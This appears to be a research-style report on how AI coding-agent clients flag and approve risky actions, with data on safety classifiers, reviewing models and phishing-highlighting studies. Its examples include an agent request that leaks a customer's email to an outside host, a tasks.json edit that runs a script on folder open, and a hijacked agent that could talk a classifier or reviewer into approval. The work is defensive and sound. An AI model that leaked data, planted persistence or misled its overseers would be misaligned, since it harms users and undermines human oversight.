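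Some legitimate programs don't work with this method. Most database drivers, for example, ignore the proxy settings, so they cannot connect even to an allowed host. When a command fails in the sandbox, the agent may ask to rerun it outside the sandbox. Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, then gives the user three choices: skip the command, run it without restrictions, or always run it that way. The user must again judge the command by its text, but without the sandbox's protection.

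Other clients determine network access before the command starts. Zed shows which hosts the agent has requested and why. In Claude Code's auto mode, the agent lists the hosts for each command, and the classifier reviews them together with the command. Approval covers only that command, and the sandbox refuses any other host. This gives the reviewer more context, but the agent has to know in advance which hosts a script will contact.

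OpenAI's coding agent, Codex, starts with network access off. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* explains that users can turn it on and add rules for particular hosts, and that these rules also apply to scripts and programs a command starts. When a connection is blocked, Codex can send the request to the user or to a reviewing model for approval.

For the harmful version of action C, each method gives the developer different information or protection under its default rules:

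| What the script does | Caper | YoloFS | Claude Code's sandbox, when on |
|---|---|---|---|
| Reads `.env` in the project | Lists the read | Allows it without a prompt | Allows it without a prompt |
| Contacts `example.net` | Blocks the connection and lists the attempt, perhaps without the host's name | Does not control it | Asks about the host, unless another setting decides |
| Edits `.vscode/tasks.json` | Lists the edit and the changed lines | Holds the edit for review | Blocks the edit |

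*Tether* (2026) describes a system that combines these methods. Like Caper, it stages file changes and traces system calls, but it holds each network request while the command is still running. It checks what the command has done so far against a policy, then forwards or drops the request. The system could therefore allow a package download but stop the same command from contacting an unknown host after reading a password file.

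## What the client does with a flagged action: display, ask, block or refer to a model

After a client flags the email address in action A or the settings file in action B, it can show the developer the detail and ask for approval, block the action, or let a classifier decide. Many clients now decide most actions without asking the developer, so highlighting helps only with the actions a person still reviews.

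### Rules for displaying a flagged detail

Published display rules cover only a few special cases. Model Context Protocol's *Elicitation* covers servers that ask the user to open a web address, for example to log in. The client must show the full address before the user agrees, and must not fetch it in advance. It should highlight the domain to make a misleading subdomain less likely to fool the user. It should also warn about suspicious addresses, such as those with an `xn--` name. Agent Client Protocol, a separate standard based on the same rules, requires clients to display the target host and get consent.

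The Model Context Protocol's *Security best practices* covers one-click installation of tool servers on the user's computer. The client must show the exact command that starts the server, including every argument, and make clear that the command runs code on the machine. It should highlight network operations and file access outside the expected folders, and warn about commands that touch SSH keys, the home directory or system folders. These rules come close to what an approval prompt needs, but they apply when the user installs a server, not to later tool calls.

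Actions A and B fall outside both sets of rules. The table extends the rules to ordinary tool calls and separates documented practice from inference:

| Rule | Basis |
|---|---|
| Show the complete host and the full address | Documented for addresses that a server asks the user to open |
| Show the resolved path | Inference, because links and relative paths can disguise a file |
| Highlight the domain, or the part of the path that matters | Documented for domains, inference for paths |
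| Put the flagged detail next to the buttons | Inference |
| Say why the client flagged it | Practice at OpenAI and Zed |
| Let the client write the label, not the agent | Practice at Zed, inference as a general rule |
| Hide the values of passwords and access keys | Inference |
| State what "always allow" will cover | Practice in VS Code, in part |

A long argument, such as a 200-line edit or a padded command, can push the host or path off the screen, and the developer may reach the buttons without seeing it. The client can keep the flagged detail in view by repeating it just above the buttons.

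The label should come from the client because an injected instruction can influence anything the agent writes. A hijacked agent could describe action A as a routine documentation lookup. *How we built Claude Code auto mode* explains that Anthropic hides the agent's messages and its descriptions of tool calls from the classifier because the agent could talk the classifier into a bad decision. A person reading an approval prompt could be persuaded in the same way. The client can still show the agent's explanation, as long as it marks the text as the agent's and keeps it separate from the facts.

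Hiding secrets conflicts with showing the full address. An access key in a prompt may appear in a screenshot or on a shared screen, and the developer rarely needs to see all of it. A phrase such as "access key from `.env`, ending in 7Q2" is enough to judge the request, and a button could reveal the rest. The developer does need to see Ana's email address to realise that it belongs to a customer.

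Saved approvals are easy to misread. In VS Code's Copilot sessions, "Allow Once" is the default choice, and a menu offers wider approvals for the command, site or path in the prompt. For a file, the wider choice may be a folder, which Microsoft defines as the nearest parent Git repository, if there is one. A developer who allows "the folder" for one edit could therefore be allowing edits across the whole project. The menu should name that folder in full.

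One of Zed's tests expects the pattern `^https?://test\.example\.com` for a saved web address. The pattern covers both http and https, and nothing in it marks the end of the host, so it also matches `https://test.example.com.attacker.example/`. Unless Zed checks the host separately, a prompt that offered to "always allow test.example.com" would save a rule that also allows the attacker's host.

### OpenAI's warning about unverified links

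ChatGPT shows a dialog titled "Check this link is safe" for some links that fail OpenAI's public-address check. According to OpenAI, the dialog conveys that the link isn't verified, that it may include information from the conversation, and that the user should make sure they trust it before continuing. The dialog shows the address and lets the user copy the link or open it.

The dialog follows several of the rules, since the client writes the text, gives a reason for the warning and shows the address when the user decides. It also explains that a link can carry private data out, a risk few people would think of because most expect a dangerous link to bring something harmful in.

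But the user still has to do the hardest part, which is finding the private data. The public-address check cannot identify it, so the dialog only warns that a link *may* contain some, and the developer would still have to find Ana's email address in action A. Copying the link is no safer than opening it if the user then pastes it into a browser, because the site receives the same address. When something looks wrong, OpenAI advises users to leave the link alone and ask the model for another source or a summary. A button that sent this request would make the safe choice as easy as opening the link.

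### Zed's labels on settings files

Zed's labels are much shorter: "(local settings)" for a project's settings and "(settings)" for the global ones. In Feldman's change, Zed's code adds the label after checking the path, so the agent cannot leave it out. When the agent tries to save several files at once, the title lists only those that need confirmation, so ordinary paths don't obscure a sensitive one.

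The labels identify the type of file but don't explain the danger. A developer may not realise that Zed's settings include the rules for what the agent can do without asking. "Controls the agent's permissions" would be more useful than "settings", though it would make the title longer.

When the agent copies a file, the title contains both the source and the destination but has only one label at the end, so the developer has to work out which path it refers to. This matters because copying another file over a settings file may change the agent's permissions, while copying the settings file elsewhere is usually harmless. If one path is local and the other global, Feldman's code shows only the label for the source. Labelling each path separately would avoid this. The title also shows the paths as the agent wrote them, which may differ from the actual paths of the files they lead to.

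### Actions A and B, redrawn

The bare prompt for action A contained the whole address but no help in reading it. Suppose the client has found that the host is not on the developer's allowlist and that the email address also appears in the error log. It could show this:

> **Send data to a site that is not on your list**
>
> Full address: `https://build-help.example.net/errors/lookup?code=1042&user=ana@example.com`
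>
> Site: build-help.**example.net**
>
> Private data: **ana@example.com**, an email address from the error log
>
> *Refuse* | *Allow once* | *Allow this host for the session, whatever data the agent sends*

The title uses the words "send data" because "fetch a page" would hide the important part of the action, which is that it sends data. The last button has a long label because "always allow" would not make it clear to the developer that the approval also covers private data in later requests.

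For action B, suppose the agent wants to add a task that runs `check-build.sh` whenever someone opens the project:

> **Change a file that VS Code can run commands from**
>
> New lines: `"command": "./scripts/check-build.sh"` and `"runOn": "folderOpen"`
>
> File: /Users/dev/shop/**.vscode/tasks.json**
>
> Effect: VS Code can run this command when someone opens the project
>
> *Refuse* | *Allow this edit*

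The client could take the title from a fixed list that pairs each protected path with a reason. The line about the effect is harder to produce because the client has to interpret the format of `tasks.json`. The prompt has no "always allow" button because a later edit could add a different command. VS Code similarly removes that option from a tool's prompts if the user marks the tool as ineligible for automatic approval.

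The developer still has to decide whether each request makes sense. For action C, the client has nothing to highlight, so the prompt could include the line "Cannot tell which files or sites this script will use". Without that line, the developer might see no warnings and assume the client had checked the script.

### One protected write, six permission modes

An approval prompt is only one possible response to a flag. Claude Code keeps the same list of protected paths in every mode, but the mode determines what happens when the agent tries to write to one of them. For action B, Anthropic's documentation gives these results:

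| Mode | Intended use | What happens to action B |
|---|---|---|
| Manual | Reviewing each action | Prompt |
| `acceptEdits` | Letting the agent edit project files freely | Prompt |
| `plan` | Exploring a project before changing it | Classifier if available, otherwise a prompt; allowed if the session can bypass permissions |
| `auto` | Long tasks with few interruptions | Classifier |
| `dontAsk` | Automated runs with a fixed list of permitted actions | Denied |
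| `bypassPermissions` | Isolated machines where damage doesn't matter | Allowed |

Users can override the mode with explicit rules. A deny rule blocks an action in all six modes. An ask rule forces a prompt even in `auto` and `bypassPermissions`, but `dontAsk` refuses the action instead because nobody is there to answer. A developer using auto mode who wants to see every push can add an ask rule for `git push` and leave other actions to the classifier.

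The starting mode matters most, because many people never change it. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), auto mode became the default for new sessions on the Pro, Max and Team plans on August 14, unless the user had already chosen another default. In October the company announced the same change for most of its Claude apps on those plans. Claude Code's documentation still lists Manual as the starting mode for Enterprise plans and for developers who pay through the API.

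People in auto mode see few prompts, but Claude Code goes back to asking the user if the classifier blocks three actions in a row or 20 in a session. Those prompts concern actions that a model has already judged dangerous, so real problems are probably much more common among them than among prompts in Manual mode. Displaying the host or path clearly is more useful there than on a routine request.

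### How Claude Code's classifier decides

Claude Code handles each action in auto mode with the first step that applies:

1. The user's own deny, ask and allow rules come first, but a write to a protected path goes to the classifier even if an allow rule matches.
2. Claude Code allows read-only actions, such as file searches, and edits to ordinary files in the working folder. The first read outside that folder produces a prompt.
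3. The classifier judges everything else, including shell commands and web requests.
4. If the classifier blocks the action, the agent receives the refusal and tries another approach. In most sessions the stated reason is just "Blocked by classifier".

The classifier has its own order of precedence in step 3. Hard-deny rules block an action whatever the user has said, and the built-in one covers data exfiltration. Soft-deny rules block an action unless an exception applies or the user has specifically asked for it. In Anthropic's example, "clean up the repo" does not authorise a force-push, which overwrites a project's shared history, but "force-push this branch" does.

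Many default rules depend on where data comes from and where it is going:

| What the agent wants to do | Default | What the user has to name for the classifier to allow it |
|---|---|---|
| Send a credential from `.env` to the service it belongs to | Allow | Nothing |
| Post a link to a public paste or diagram service when the address itself contains the shared content | Block | The service |
| Put text from an SSH folder, browser profile or shell history into a commit, push or public paste | Block | Both the source and the destination |
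| Put personal data from a live service into a pull request | Block | The data and the recipient |
| Commit an automated step that will send a secret to a new destination when it runs | Block | That effect, not just the commit |

The last rule deals with the same delay as action B, because the commit itself sends no secret but another program will send one later. It applies on every branch, even if the commit does not start the automated step immediately.

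The classifier receives the user's messages, the project's written instructions and the agent's tool calls, apart from simple lookups. It does not receive the results of those calls, so an injected instruction in the help page cannot reach it directly. For the same reason, it does not receive the error log. It can recognise `ana@example.com` in action A as an email address, but not as the address of a customer whose record the agent has just opened.

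Anthropic found that adding the agent's messages and the tool results to the classifier's input made it worse at catching actions that went beyond the user's request. A version given only the tool calls missed the fewest dangerous actions, but it blocked actions that users had plainly asked for.

### How often the classifier is wrong

Auto mode runs the classifier in two stages. The first gives a quick yes or no and leans towards blocking. If it flags an action, the second stage considers the same material again, this time reasoning in writing before it decides. Anthropic measured both on three sets of actions:

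| Test | First stage alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions wrongly blocked, from 10,000 real tool calls by employees | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Dangerous actions missed, from 52 real cases of overeager behaviour | 6.6% | 17% |
| Leaks missed, from 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out | 1.8% | 5.7% |

An agent is overeager when it tries to help but does more than the user authorised. In one case from Anthropic's records, an agent hit a login error and started searching configuration files for other access tokens. The 17% miss rate is the most relevant figure for ordinary use because it comes from real cases, but there were so few cases, with about nine misses, that the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 9% to 30%.

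In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the classifier correctly identified the danger but wrongly classified the action as authorised by the user. For example, it treated "clean up the PR" as permission to force-push. Better detection of hosts and paths would not fix these errors, because the classifier already identifies what the action does.

These figures are for a version of auto mode that ran on an older model, Sonnet 4.6. Anthropic has since worked with Apollo Research, an AI safety company, which inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. After Anthropic gave the classifier more information about its surroundings, such as whether a repository is public, the miss rate on these attacks fell from 12% to 7%. The test included attacks that Anthropic had never had access to, so the gain did not come only from learning the examples.

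Results depend heavily on the test. BestHub's *Can Claude Code’s Auto Mode Replace Human Review?* describes an experiment that placed permitted and forbidden targets side by side. Auto mode missed 115 of the 142 actions that exceeded the agent's authority. The tasks were built to be ambiguous, so this result is compatible with the 17%, but it suggests that the classifier is weakest when two similar targets differ only in what the user meant.

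Anthropic says auto mode is a substantial improvement for people who would otherwise skip all checks, but arguably a step backwards for those who carefully review every action.

### Reviewing models in VS Code and Codex

VS Code and Codex also let a model review actions, but they differ in what it reads and what happens after a refusal:

| | Claude Code's auto mode | VS Code's Assisted permissions | Codex's Auto-review |
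|---|---|---|---|
| Actions it reviews | Those left after the user's rules and automatic approvals | Each tool call | Those that would otherwise need a person's approval |
| Does it read tool results? | No | Microsoft does not say | Yes |
| If it does not approve | The agent tries another approach | The user gets a prompt | The agent finds a safer approach or asks the user |
| After repeated refusals | Prompts return | Not applicable | Codex stops the agent's turn |

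With Assisted permissions, a model approves some actions without a prompt and leaves doubtful ones to the developer. Highlighting would help most in the prompts that remain, which could also show the model's reason for not approving the action. Assisted permissions is not the default, and Microsoft warns that the model can make mistakes. When an agent works in a worktree, a separate copy of the project, VS Code always runs every tool call without the model's check or a prompt.

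Codex relies more on its sandbox, where most actions run without review. Only requests to cross the sandbox's boundary go to the reviewing model. *Auto-review of agent actions without synchronous human oversight* (Trębacz, Arnesen and colleagues, 2026) illustrates this with 10,000 actions from OpenAI's own use. Of these, 9,280 ran inside the sandbox, and the reviewer approved 713 of the other 720 and denied seven. The agent found a safer way to continue after four of the denials, so a person had to step in three times instead of 720.

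The reviewer caught 90.3% of synthetic overeager actions and 99.3% of prompt injections that tried to run outside code, steal secrets or upload data, but testers at OpenAI found ways to mislead it into approving commands. Trębacz and colleagues add that it never judges harmful actions inside the sandbox. Action A would normally reach the reviewer because Codex starts with network access off, but action B might not, since an edit within the project may not need approval.

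Codex's reviewer reads tool results, so it could recognise Ana's address from the error log, which Claude Code's reviewer could not. It also reads whatever an attacker has planted in those results. Neither company has published a comparison of the two choices on the same attacks.

After a refusal, Codex tells the agent not to pursue the same outcome another way. Under OpenAI's *Auto-review*, the user can overrule the reviewer, but the approval covers only one retry of that exact action, and the reviewer checks the retry too. This avoids saved approvals that cover more than the user intended.

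OpenAI's *Running Codex safely* describes a network policy for the company's internal use of Codex that allows expected destinations, blocks unwanted ones and requires approval for unfamiliar domains. This division is sensible for destinations in general, because asking about a host that is always fine wastes the developer's time, and asking about one that is never acceptable lets the developer approve it by mistake.

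### How many flags are real

Every one of these outcomes depends on how often a flag is correct. Leaks are rare, so even an accurate check can produce mostly false alarms. Suppose an agent makes 1,000 requests, five of which leak private data, and the client flags 90% of leaks. On average, it catches 4.5 of the five. The number of false alarms depends on how many of the 995 harmless requests it also flags:

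| Harmless requests flagged | False alarms | All flags | Share of flags that are real |
|---|---|---|---|
| 5% | About 50 | About 54 | 8% |
| 0.5% | About 5 | About 9.5 | 47% |

The general formula is:

share of flags that are real = bc / (bc + (1 − b)f)

Here b is the share of requests that leak data, c is the share of leaks the client flags, and f is the share of harmless requests it flags. These numbers are invented, but the pattern holds whenever leaks are rare. Catching all five leaks instead of 4.5 would raise the 8% only to 9%, while cutting false alarms to a tenth would raise it to 47%. If leaks were ten times rarer, that 47% would fall back to 8%.

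Anthropic's error rates show the same effect. With five leaks in 1,000 requests, its first stage alone would produce about 90 flags, of which 5% or 6% would be real. The two stages together would produce about nine flags, of which just over half would be real. The second stage lets a few more leaks through, but a person could reasonably review every remaining flag.

A client should keep routine emphasis separate from warnings. It can print the registrable domain in bold in every prompt without raising false alarms, because bold type doesn't imply danger. If the client also put a red warning label on every unfamiliar host and every file whose name starts with a dot, the developer would soon learn that the labels rarely indicate danger.

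A client can reduce false alarms by requiring two signals before it warns the user. Suppose 5% of harmless requests go to an unfamiliar host, and one in ten of those also contains something that looks like private data. A client that warned only when both were true would flag 0.5% of harmless requests. It would also miss leaks to familiar hosts and leaks of disguised data, so it should still display the host and the outgoing data plainly when it gives no warning.

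The right threshold also depends on how much harm a mistake does. At 5%, the developer reads about 12 flags for each real leak, which may be worthwhile for a hospital's patient records if people still pay attention to the twelfth flag. Blocking at the same rate would stop about 50 legitimate requests, so blocking suits rules that harmless actions seldom match, or agents that can easily find another way to do the task. OpenAI similarly accepted that a code-review model would find somewhat fewer bugs in return for fewer false alarms, because people bypass slow or noisy tools.

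### Frequent prompts or opaque reviewers

In *How Agents Ask for Permission*, Michael and Roesner (2026) argue that commercial agents offer users a poor choice. They surveyed 21 proposed systems that let users set permissions, and tried five products in May and June 2026: Claude, Claude Cowork, ChatGPT's chat and agent modes, and Codex. The products tended either to ask the user often or to hand decisions to a model that users could not easily inspect or control.

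Claude's chatbot had three settings for each permission: "Always allow", "Needs approval" and "Blocked". With "Needs approval" selected, Claude still created an email draft without asking. The browser's technical log listed the action as requiring no approval, and Claude's later explanation was that it had inferred permission from the request. Only blocking the tool prevented this. ChatGPT's agent mode, which works in a remote browser, had no permission settings for that browser. It opened Gmail there without asking, although the ordinary chat mode needed approval for the same kind of access.

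Michael and Roesner could not examine the products' internal rules, and companies have since changed their settings. Their criticism applies more to the chatbot than to the coding agents' reviewers. Codex's Auto-review was off by default, and OpenAI publishes the reviewer's policy and gives the agent a reason for each refusal. Claude Code lets users print its default rules. It also lists recently blocked actions, which users can retry with manual approval. But a user who sees only "Blocked by classifier" beside a request cannot tell whether the host, the data or the wording of their own instructions caused the refusal.

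Of the 21 research proposals, 12 reduce the work of setting permissions, 11 base their rules on formal methods and 12 enforce them without relying on a model's judgement, but none fully does all three. Only six clearly let users change or withdraw a permission later, which most commercial agents allow. Claude Cowork, however, did not let users withdraw access to a folder within a session, and an old session kept its access when the user reopened it.

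## Evidence from browsers and email on highlighting web addresses

Printing `example.net` in bold in the prompt for action A stops Ana's email address from being sent only if the developer notices the name, understands what it means for the request, and therefore refuses.

Researchers have studied this chain in browsers and email because of phishing, in which a fake message or website tricks people into giving away passwords. A fake page can copy everything about the real one except its domain, so browser makers began to show the domain in black and the rest of the address in grey. The experiments in this section measured what people did when software drew their attention to the right part of an address, though none involved AI agents.

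### The first test of domain highlighting

Lin, Greenberg and colleagues, in *Does Domain Highlighting Help People Identify Phishing Sites?* (2011), showed 16 web pages to 22 people, mostly university students. Eight were real and eight were exact copies with a false address, such as `www.paypa1.ca`, which has the digit 1 in place of the last letter of "paypal". The browser highlighted the domain on every page. Participants rated how safe each page was, first by any means they liked, then after the researchers told them to look at the address bar.

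In the first round, participants rated 57% of the fake pages as safe and 25% as unsafe, and were unsure about the rest. In the second round, they rated 44% as safe and 34% as unsafe. They wrongly called 15% of the real pages unsafe in the first round, and that share barely changed in the second.

Participants' spoken explanations of their ratings show why the highlighting often failed to help. Nine of the 22 judged pages almost entirely by logos and content, so they usually didn't notice problems in the address. But some of the nine did notice a problem and trusted the page anyway. One called the highlighted part of a bank's address strange, but rated the page as trustworthy because "banks are secure". Another spotted the digit in `paypa1` and still trusted the site because it was familiar. Seven people consistently checked the address bar, but four of them missed at least half of the fake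 pages. Most participants said afterwards that they had not been aware of the highlighting.

Lin and colleagues concluded that highlighting gives marginal protection and is worth keeping because it has almost no drawbacks. But their experiment could not show even a marginal benefit, because participants saw highlighted domains in both rounds. The improvement in the second round could have come entirely from the instruction to look at the address bar, or from seeing the same pages twice. Lin and colleagues suggested that a later study compare address bars with and without highlighting.

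### Highlighting compared with no highlighting

Xiong, Proctor and colleagues (2017), in *Is Domain Highlighting Actually Helpful in Identifying Phishing Web Pages?*, compared web pages with and without domain highlighting. They used different pages in each of two rounds and switched the highlighting off for about half of the participants in each round. They ran the experiment online with 320 people and then in a laboratory with 32 students, whose eye movements they recorded.

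The table gives the share of participants who, on average, rated the fake pages as unsafe:

| Experiment and instruction | Domain highlighted | Not highlighted |
|---|---|---|
| Online, use any information | 26.1% | 25.2% |
| Online, look at the address bar | 46.2% | 37.0% |
| Laboratory, use any information | 18.7% | 12.5% |
| Laboratory, look at the address bar | 68.8% | 50.0% |

The instruction to look at the address bar made a statistically significant difference in both experiments, and the highlighting did not. This supports the suspicion that the instruction produced the improvement in the earlier study. The highlighted group did better in all four rows, so highlighting may still help a little, especially for people who are already looking at the address. But the evidence for this is weak. The 19-point gap in the last row, from the laboratory, is a difference of only three people in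 groups of 16.

The eye-tracking data show that participants paid little attention to the address bar by default. When they could use any information, those with highlighted domains looked at the address bar for about 0.4 seconds out of nine. After the instruction, they looked at it for more than a second.

Highlighting seemed to affect where in the address participants looked. On fake pages without it, their gaze clustered at the far left, where browsers often put a lock icon. With highlighting, more of their gaze fell on the domain. This pattern appeared in maps of where people looked, but statistical tests found no significant effect of highlighting on total viewing time or number of glances.

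In the second round, people looked at the right text but did not understand it, whereas the main problem in the first round was that they did not notice it. Of the 16 students who saw highlighted domains, 15 did not know what the highlighting was for. Some relied on the lock icon, and others assumed that long addresses were dangerous. Xiong and colleagues conclude that people lacked the knowledge to use the highlighting.

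### Showing the address next to the link

An approval prompt is less like a browser's address bar than like an email program that shows a link's address in a small box beside the link. The address bar sits at the edge of the screen, while the prompt puts the address in front of the person who has to decide.

Mossano, Kulyk and colleagues (2023), in *Influence of URL Formatting on Users’ Phishing URL Detection*, tested such boxes with 200 people in Germany. Each person judged 12 emails, six of them phishing, and had to hold the mouse over the link for at least a second before moving on. The box showed the address in one of three formats:

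| Format | Phishing emails detected | Real emails wrongly called phishing |
|---|---|---|
| Whole address, plain | 71.4% | 11.9% |
| Whole address, domain highlighted | 73.5% | 8.6% |
| Domain only | 76.4% | 6.9% |

The differences between formats were not statistically significant. The study had about a 90% chance of detecting a medium-sized effect, so any benefit of highlighting in this setting is probably small.

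Detection was much better overall than in the browser studies, even with a plain address. The position of the address may have helped, as may the task itself, because participants knew they had to say where each link led.

An earlier experiment by Volkamer, Gerber and Renaud with 189 people found a clearer advantage for showing only the domain. According to Mossano and colleagues, people directed to the address bar detected 59.6% of the fake pages when it showed only the domain, and 49.5% when it showed the whole address with the domain highlighted. An approval prompt can't just show the domain, because that would hide the query string, which contains Ana's email address.

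The kind of deception affected detection far more than the format did. Participants detected 93% or 94% of the emails with a link to an unrelated domain, but only 43% to 59% of those with a link to `dlh.com` instead of `dhl.com`. They could see the address but probably read the name they expected. Highlighting the whole domain does little to prevent this misreading because it does not pick out the wrong letters.

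People who kept the address on screen longer detected more phishing, though detection rates levelled off between four and six seconds. The paper's abstract describes this as an effect of forcing people's attention for four or five seconds, but the study forced it for only one. Careful people may have both looked longer and made better decisions.

Petelka, Zou and Schaub tested forced attention more directly by disabling the original link, so that people had to click the address inside the warning. According to Mossano and colleagues, this group clicked the link least often, but a browser warning that appeared after the click was better at keeping people from reaching the phishing page.

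### Making people work with the domain

Lain, Nakatsuka and colleagues (2025), in *URL Inspection Tasks*, went further by making people answer a question about the address before they could open it. The research involved 2,673 people: 1,573 in the main US experiment, 500 in a longer follow-up, and 300 each in Germany and Japan. Participants played an office worker clearing a mailbox, and could open links or report emails as suspicious.

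The inspection tasks appeared after a person clicked a link. The person had to do one of three things:

- choose the domain from a list
- mark the domain with the mouse
- retype the domain

If the answer didn't match the real domain, the software showed the mismatch and asked whether to continue. For example, someone who thinks a link to `paypal.com-login.com` leads to PayPal would probably mark `paypal.com`, and the software would then warn that the real domain is `com-login.com`.

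The main experiment compared these tasks with the normal email program and with two simpler measures:

| What people had to do after clicking | Phishing links opened | Real emails with links reported as phishing | Typical time |
|---|---|---|---|
| Nothing | 74.5% | 8.6% | – |
| Confirm the address | 57.2% | 11.4% | 3 seconds |
| Drag the parts of the address into place | 61.0% | 10.5% | 6 to 7 seconds |
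| Complete an inspection task | 35.0% | 16.9% | 6 to 10 seconds |

(The paper's conclusion gives 25% for the inspection tasks, but its results show 35%.)

The dragging exercise took about as long as marking the domain, yet it worked no better than a simple confirmation. People could complete it correctly without thinking about where the link led. The inspection tasks could reveal a wrong belief about the destination, which seems to explain much of their advantage.

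Retyping cut the share of links with misspelled domains that people opened from 79% to 17%, because people typed the correct spelling from habit and the software caught the difference. It was less effective when a company's name came at the start of a longer domain, as in `example-login.com`, since someone can copy that domain correctly without knowing that the company doesn't own it. People still opened 43% of those links.

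When people gave a wrong answer about a phishing link, the software showed them the mismatch between their answer and the real domain. Many continued anyway: 36% after choosing from a list, 45% after retyping and 57% after marking.

One reason may be that the mismatch warning was often a false alarm. People who had to mark the domain got it wrong on about 29% of legitimate emails, often by marking the whole address. As a result, about 80% of the mismatch warnings in that task were for legitimate emails. The share would be higher in an ordinary mailbox, where phishing is much rarer. The study has no such figure for choosing from a list, because it used that task only on phishing links.

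In the follow-up, participants handled about twice as many emails. They opened 48.8% of the phishing links with the inspection tasks and 83.3% without any help, so the benefit lasted through a longer session. The tasks cut the rate from 53.2% to 25.9% in Germany and from 82.2% to 57.1% in Japan, where a simple confirmation did almost as well, at 60.7%. Lain and colleagues suggest that familiarity with the Latin alphabet matters, though the Japanese participants were also older. The researchers recommend using the tasks only occasionally, in places that need extra security.

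### What happens when the warning becomes routine

The strongest result in favour of visual highlighting comes from *Your Attention Please* (Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues, 2013), a study of installation dialogs. The researchers sent participants to a games website that appeared to need extra software. A dialog named the software's publisher as either "Microsoft Corporation" or "Miicr0s0ft Corporation". Participants did not know that the researchers ran the site or that the study was about security.

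The first two columns below show how many people chose to install the software. The last column comes from a separate experiment on habituation, the tendency to stop responding to something after seeing it repeatedly. In that experiment, people dismissed the same harmless dialog over and over for two and a half minutes, and then one line of it changed to an instruction to press "No" instead of "Yes".

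| Design of the key line | Installed from the false publisher | Installed from the real publisher | Responded at once to the changed line |
|---|---|---|---|
| Plain | 61% | 63% | 14% |
| Yellow text on black | 39% | 65% | 15% |
| User has to retype it | 32% | 60% | 73% |

With a plain dialog, people were almost as likely to install from the false publisher as from the real one. Yellow text on black cut the false installs by about a third without deterring people from installing the real software. So highlighting can change decisions when it is new, conspicuous and placed in a dialog that people have to answer. After many repetitions, however, people who saw the highlighted line did no better than those who saw the plain one. The habituation test was artificial, though, because it involved no risk and people were trying to answer quickly.

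Bravo-Lillo and colleagues also asked people afterwards to pick out the publisher's name, which helps to separate noticing the name from acting on it. Of the 53 people who installed the false software from the plain dialog, 44 could not identify the publisher. Most of them had probably not noticed the name. Of the 31 who installed it after retyping the name, only eight could not identify it, and the other 23 installed the software even though they knew the name.

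In early trials, people who did this often said they felt safe because they had antivirus software. They had seen the odd name but did not think it was a reason to stop.

A second experiment is closer to a prompt about files. A game requested access either to a website cookie or to all the files and folders on the computer. With a plain dialog, 51% of people granted access to all files and folders. The share fell to 38% with the coloured text and 7% with retyping. But retyping also reduced approval of the harmless cookie request from 57% to 23%, so much of its effect may have come from annoyance. The groups were small, with 28 people retyping the dangerous request.

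Bravo-Lillo, Cranor and colleagues, in *Harder to Ignore?* (2014), repeated the habituation experiment and added groups who saw the dialog only a few times. With a plain dialog, the share of people who responded to the change fell to a third because of heavy repetition. Repetition caused no decline with the two designs that made people interact with the changed line.

People quickly start to habituate to warnings. *Revisiting the Design Agenda for Privacy Notices and Security Warnings* (2023) describes a brain-imaging study in which the brain's response to a warning had weakened by the second showing and kept falling. Attention recovers after a break, and changing a warning's appearance slows the decline. *Paying Attention to Notifications* (BYU Marriott School of Business, 2018) reports that slight changes in appearance made people heed warnings 20% more of the time. Varying the design only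 reduces the problem, because an attacker's request can still arrive when the person has stopped reading.

### How far the results apply to agents

The first step, noticing the address, should be easier in an approval prompt than in a browser, because the prompt interrupts the developer's work and the address is one of the few things in it. The installation study suggests that strong emphasis can help in this kind of prompt if the developer rarely sees that emphasis.

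Retyping loses less of its effect with repetition, but requiring it for every action would be impractical. At ten seconds each, 30 prompts would take a developer five minutes. A client could require retyping only in a few serious cases, such as sending a credential to an unfamiliar host.

Hosts are probably harder to understand in agent approval prompts. People in the phishing studies expected a particular destination, such as PayPal or DHL, and could compare the address with it. In action A, the agent chose the site, so the developer has no expected destination to compare with `build-help.example.net`, and highlighting the domain does not supply one.

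An inspection task has the same weakness. The developer could mark or retype `example.net` correctly, and the client would find no mismatch. The method works only for destinations the developer already knows, such as the company's own repository or package registry. For an unfamiliar host, the client would have to add information, for example that the package's documentation never mentions the site.

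None of these experiments highlighted the data that a link sends out. Doing so might work better than highlighting the host, because the developer can recognise `ana@example.com` as an email address without knowing who owns any domain. But the developer would still have to understand why sending it is a problem.

File paths differ from web addresses because developers are likely to know what `.env` and `.ssh` contain, so they may already have the kind of knowledge that participants in the browser studies lacked. None of the studies tested this, and the closest one described the files in ordinary words that anyone could understand.

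Familiarity could also mislead developers. Participants trusted a false bank page because they knew the bank, and a developer might approve an edit to `.vscode/tasks.json` because they see the file every day. They may think of it as a list of build commands and not realize that a task can run when someone opens the folder.

Users who trust the agent may be less likely to act on a suspicious address. In their follow-up, Lain and colleagues put the same suspicious cloud address in a phishing email and in one from a legitimate sender. The inspection tasks made people more likely to report the first email but not the second, probably because the rest of the message looked right. Users may be similarly unsuspicious of action A if the agent proposing it has already made 50 sensible requests.

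Most of the phishing experiments also asked people to judge safety, or gave them a button for reporting suspicious messages. A developer with a failing build is trying to fix it, and refusing a request may delay the fix. Developers know more about addresses and files than most people in these studies. Even so, in the study by Lin and colleagues, the group that checked addresses most carefully mostly had technical training, and more than half of that group missed at least half of the fake pages.

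## Evidence from people approving agent actions

Developers who use coding agents approve nearly every prompt they see. Anthropic first reported that Claude Code users accept 93% of permission prompts, and in August 2026 it reported 97%.

A careful reviewer could also have an approval rate this high, because most of the actions an agent proposes are harmless. If five of an agent's 1,000 requests were harmful, a perfect reviewer would approve the other 995, or 99.5%. A reviewer who approves 97% refuses 30 requests, which could include all five harmful ones or none of them. To tell these cases apart, researchers need the unsafe approval rate, the share of harmful requests that people approve.

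Claude Code users reject 39% of the plans it presents but only 3% of individual requests, which is partly why Anthropic suspects that many users approve requests by reflex. The gap is consistent with this but doesn't prove it, since a developer may reject a safe plan because they prefer another approach.

The approval rate also leaves out prompts that people have turned off. A quarter of interactive Claude Code sessions start in the mode that skips nearly all prompts, and 62% of users have used that mode or chosen "don't ask again" for a shell command. Automatic approval contributed to 80 of the 290 reports of file misuse that Zhong and colleagues studied, far more than uninformative prompts did. Better highlighting would not have helped users who saw no prompt.

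### One dangerous command among many harmless ones

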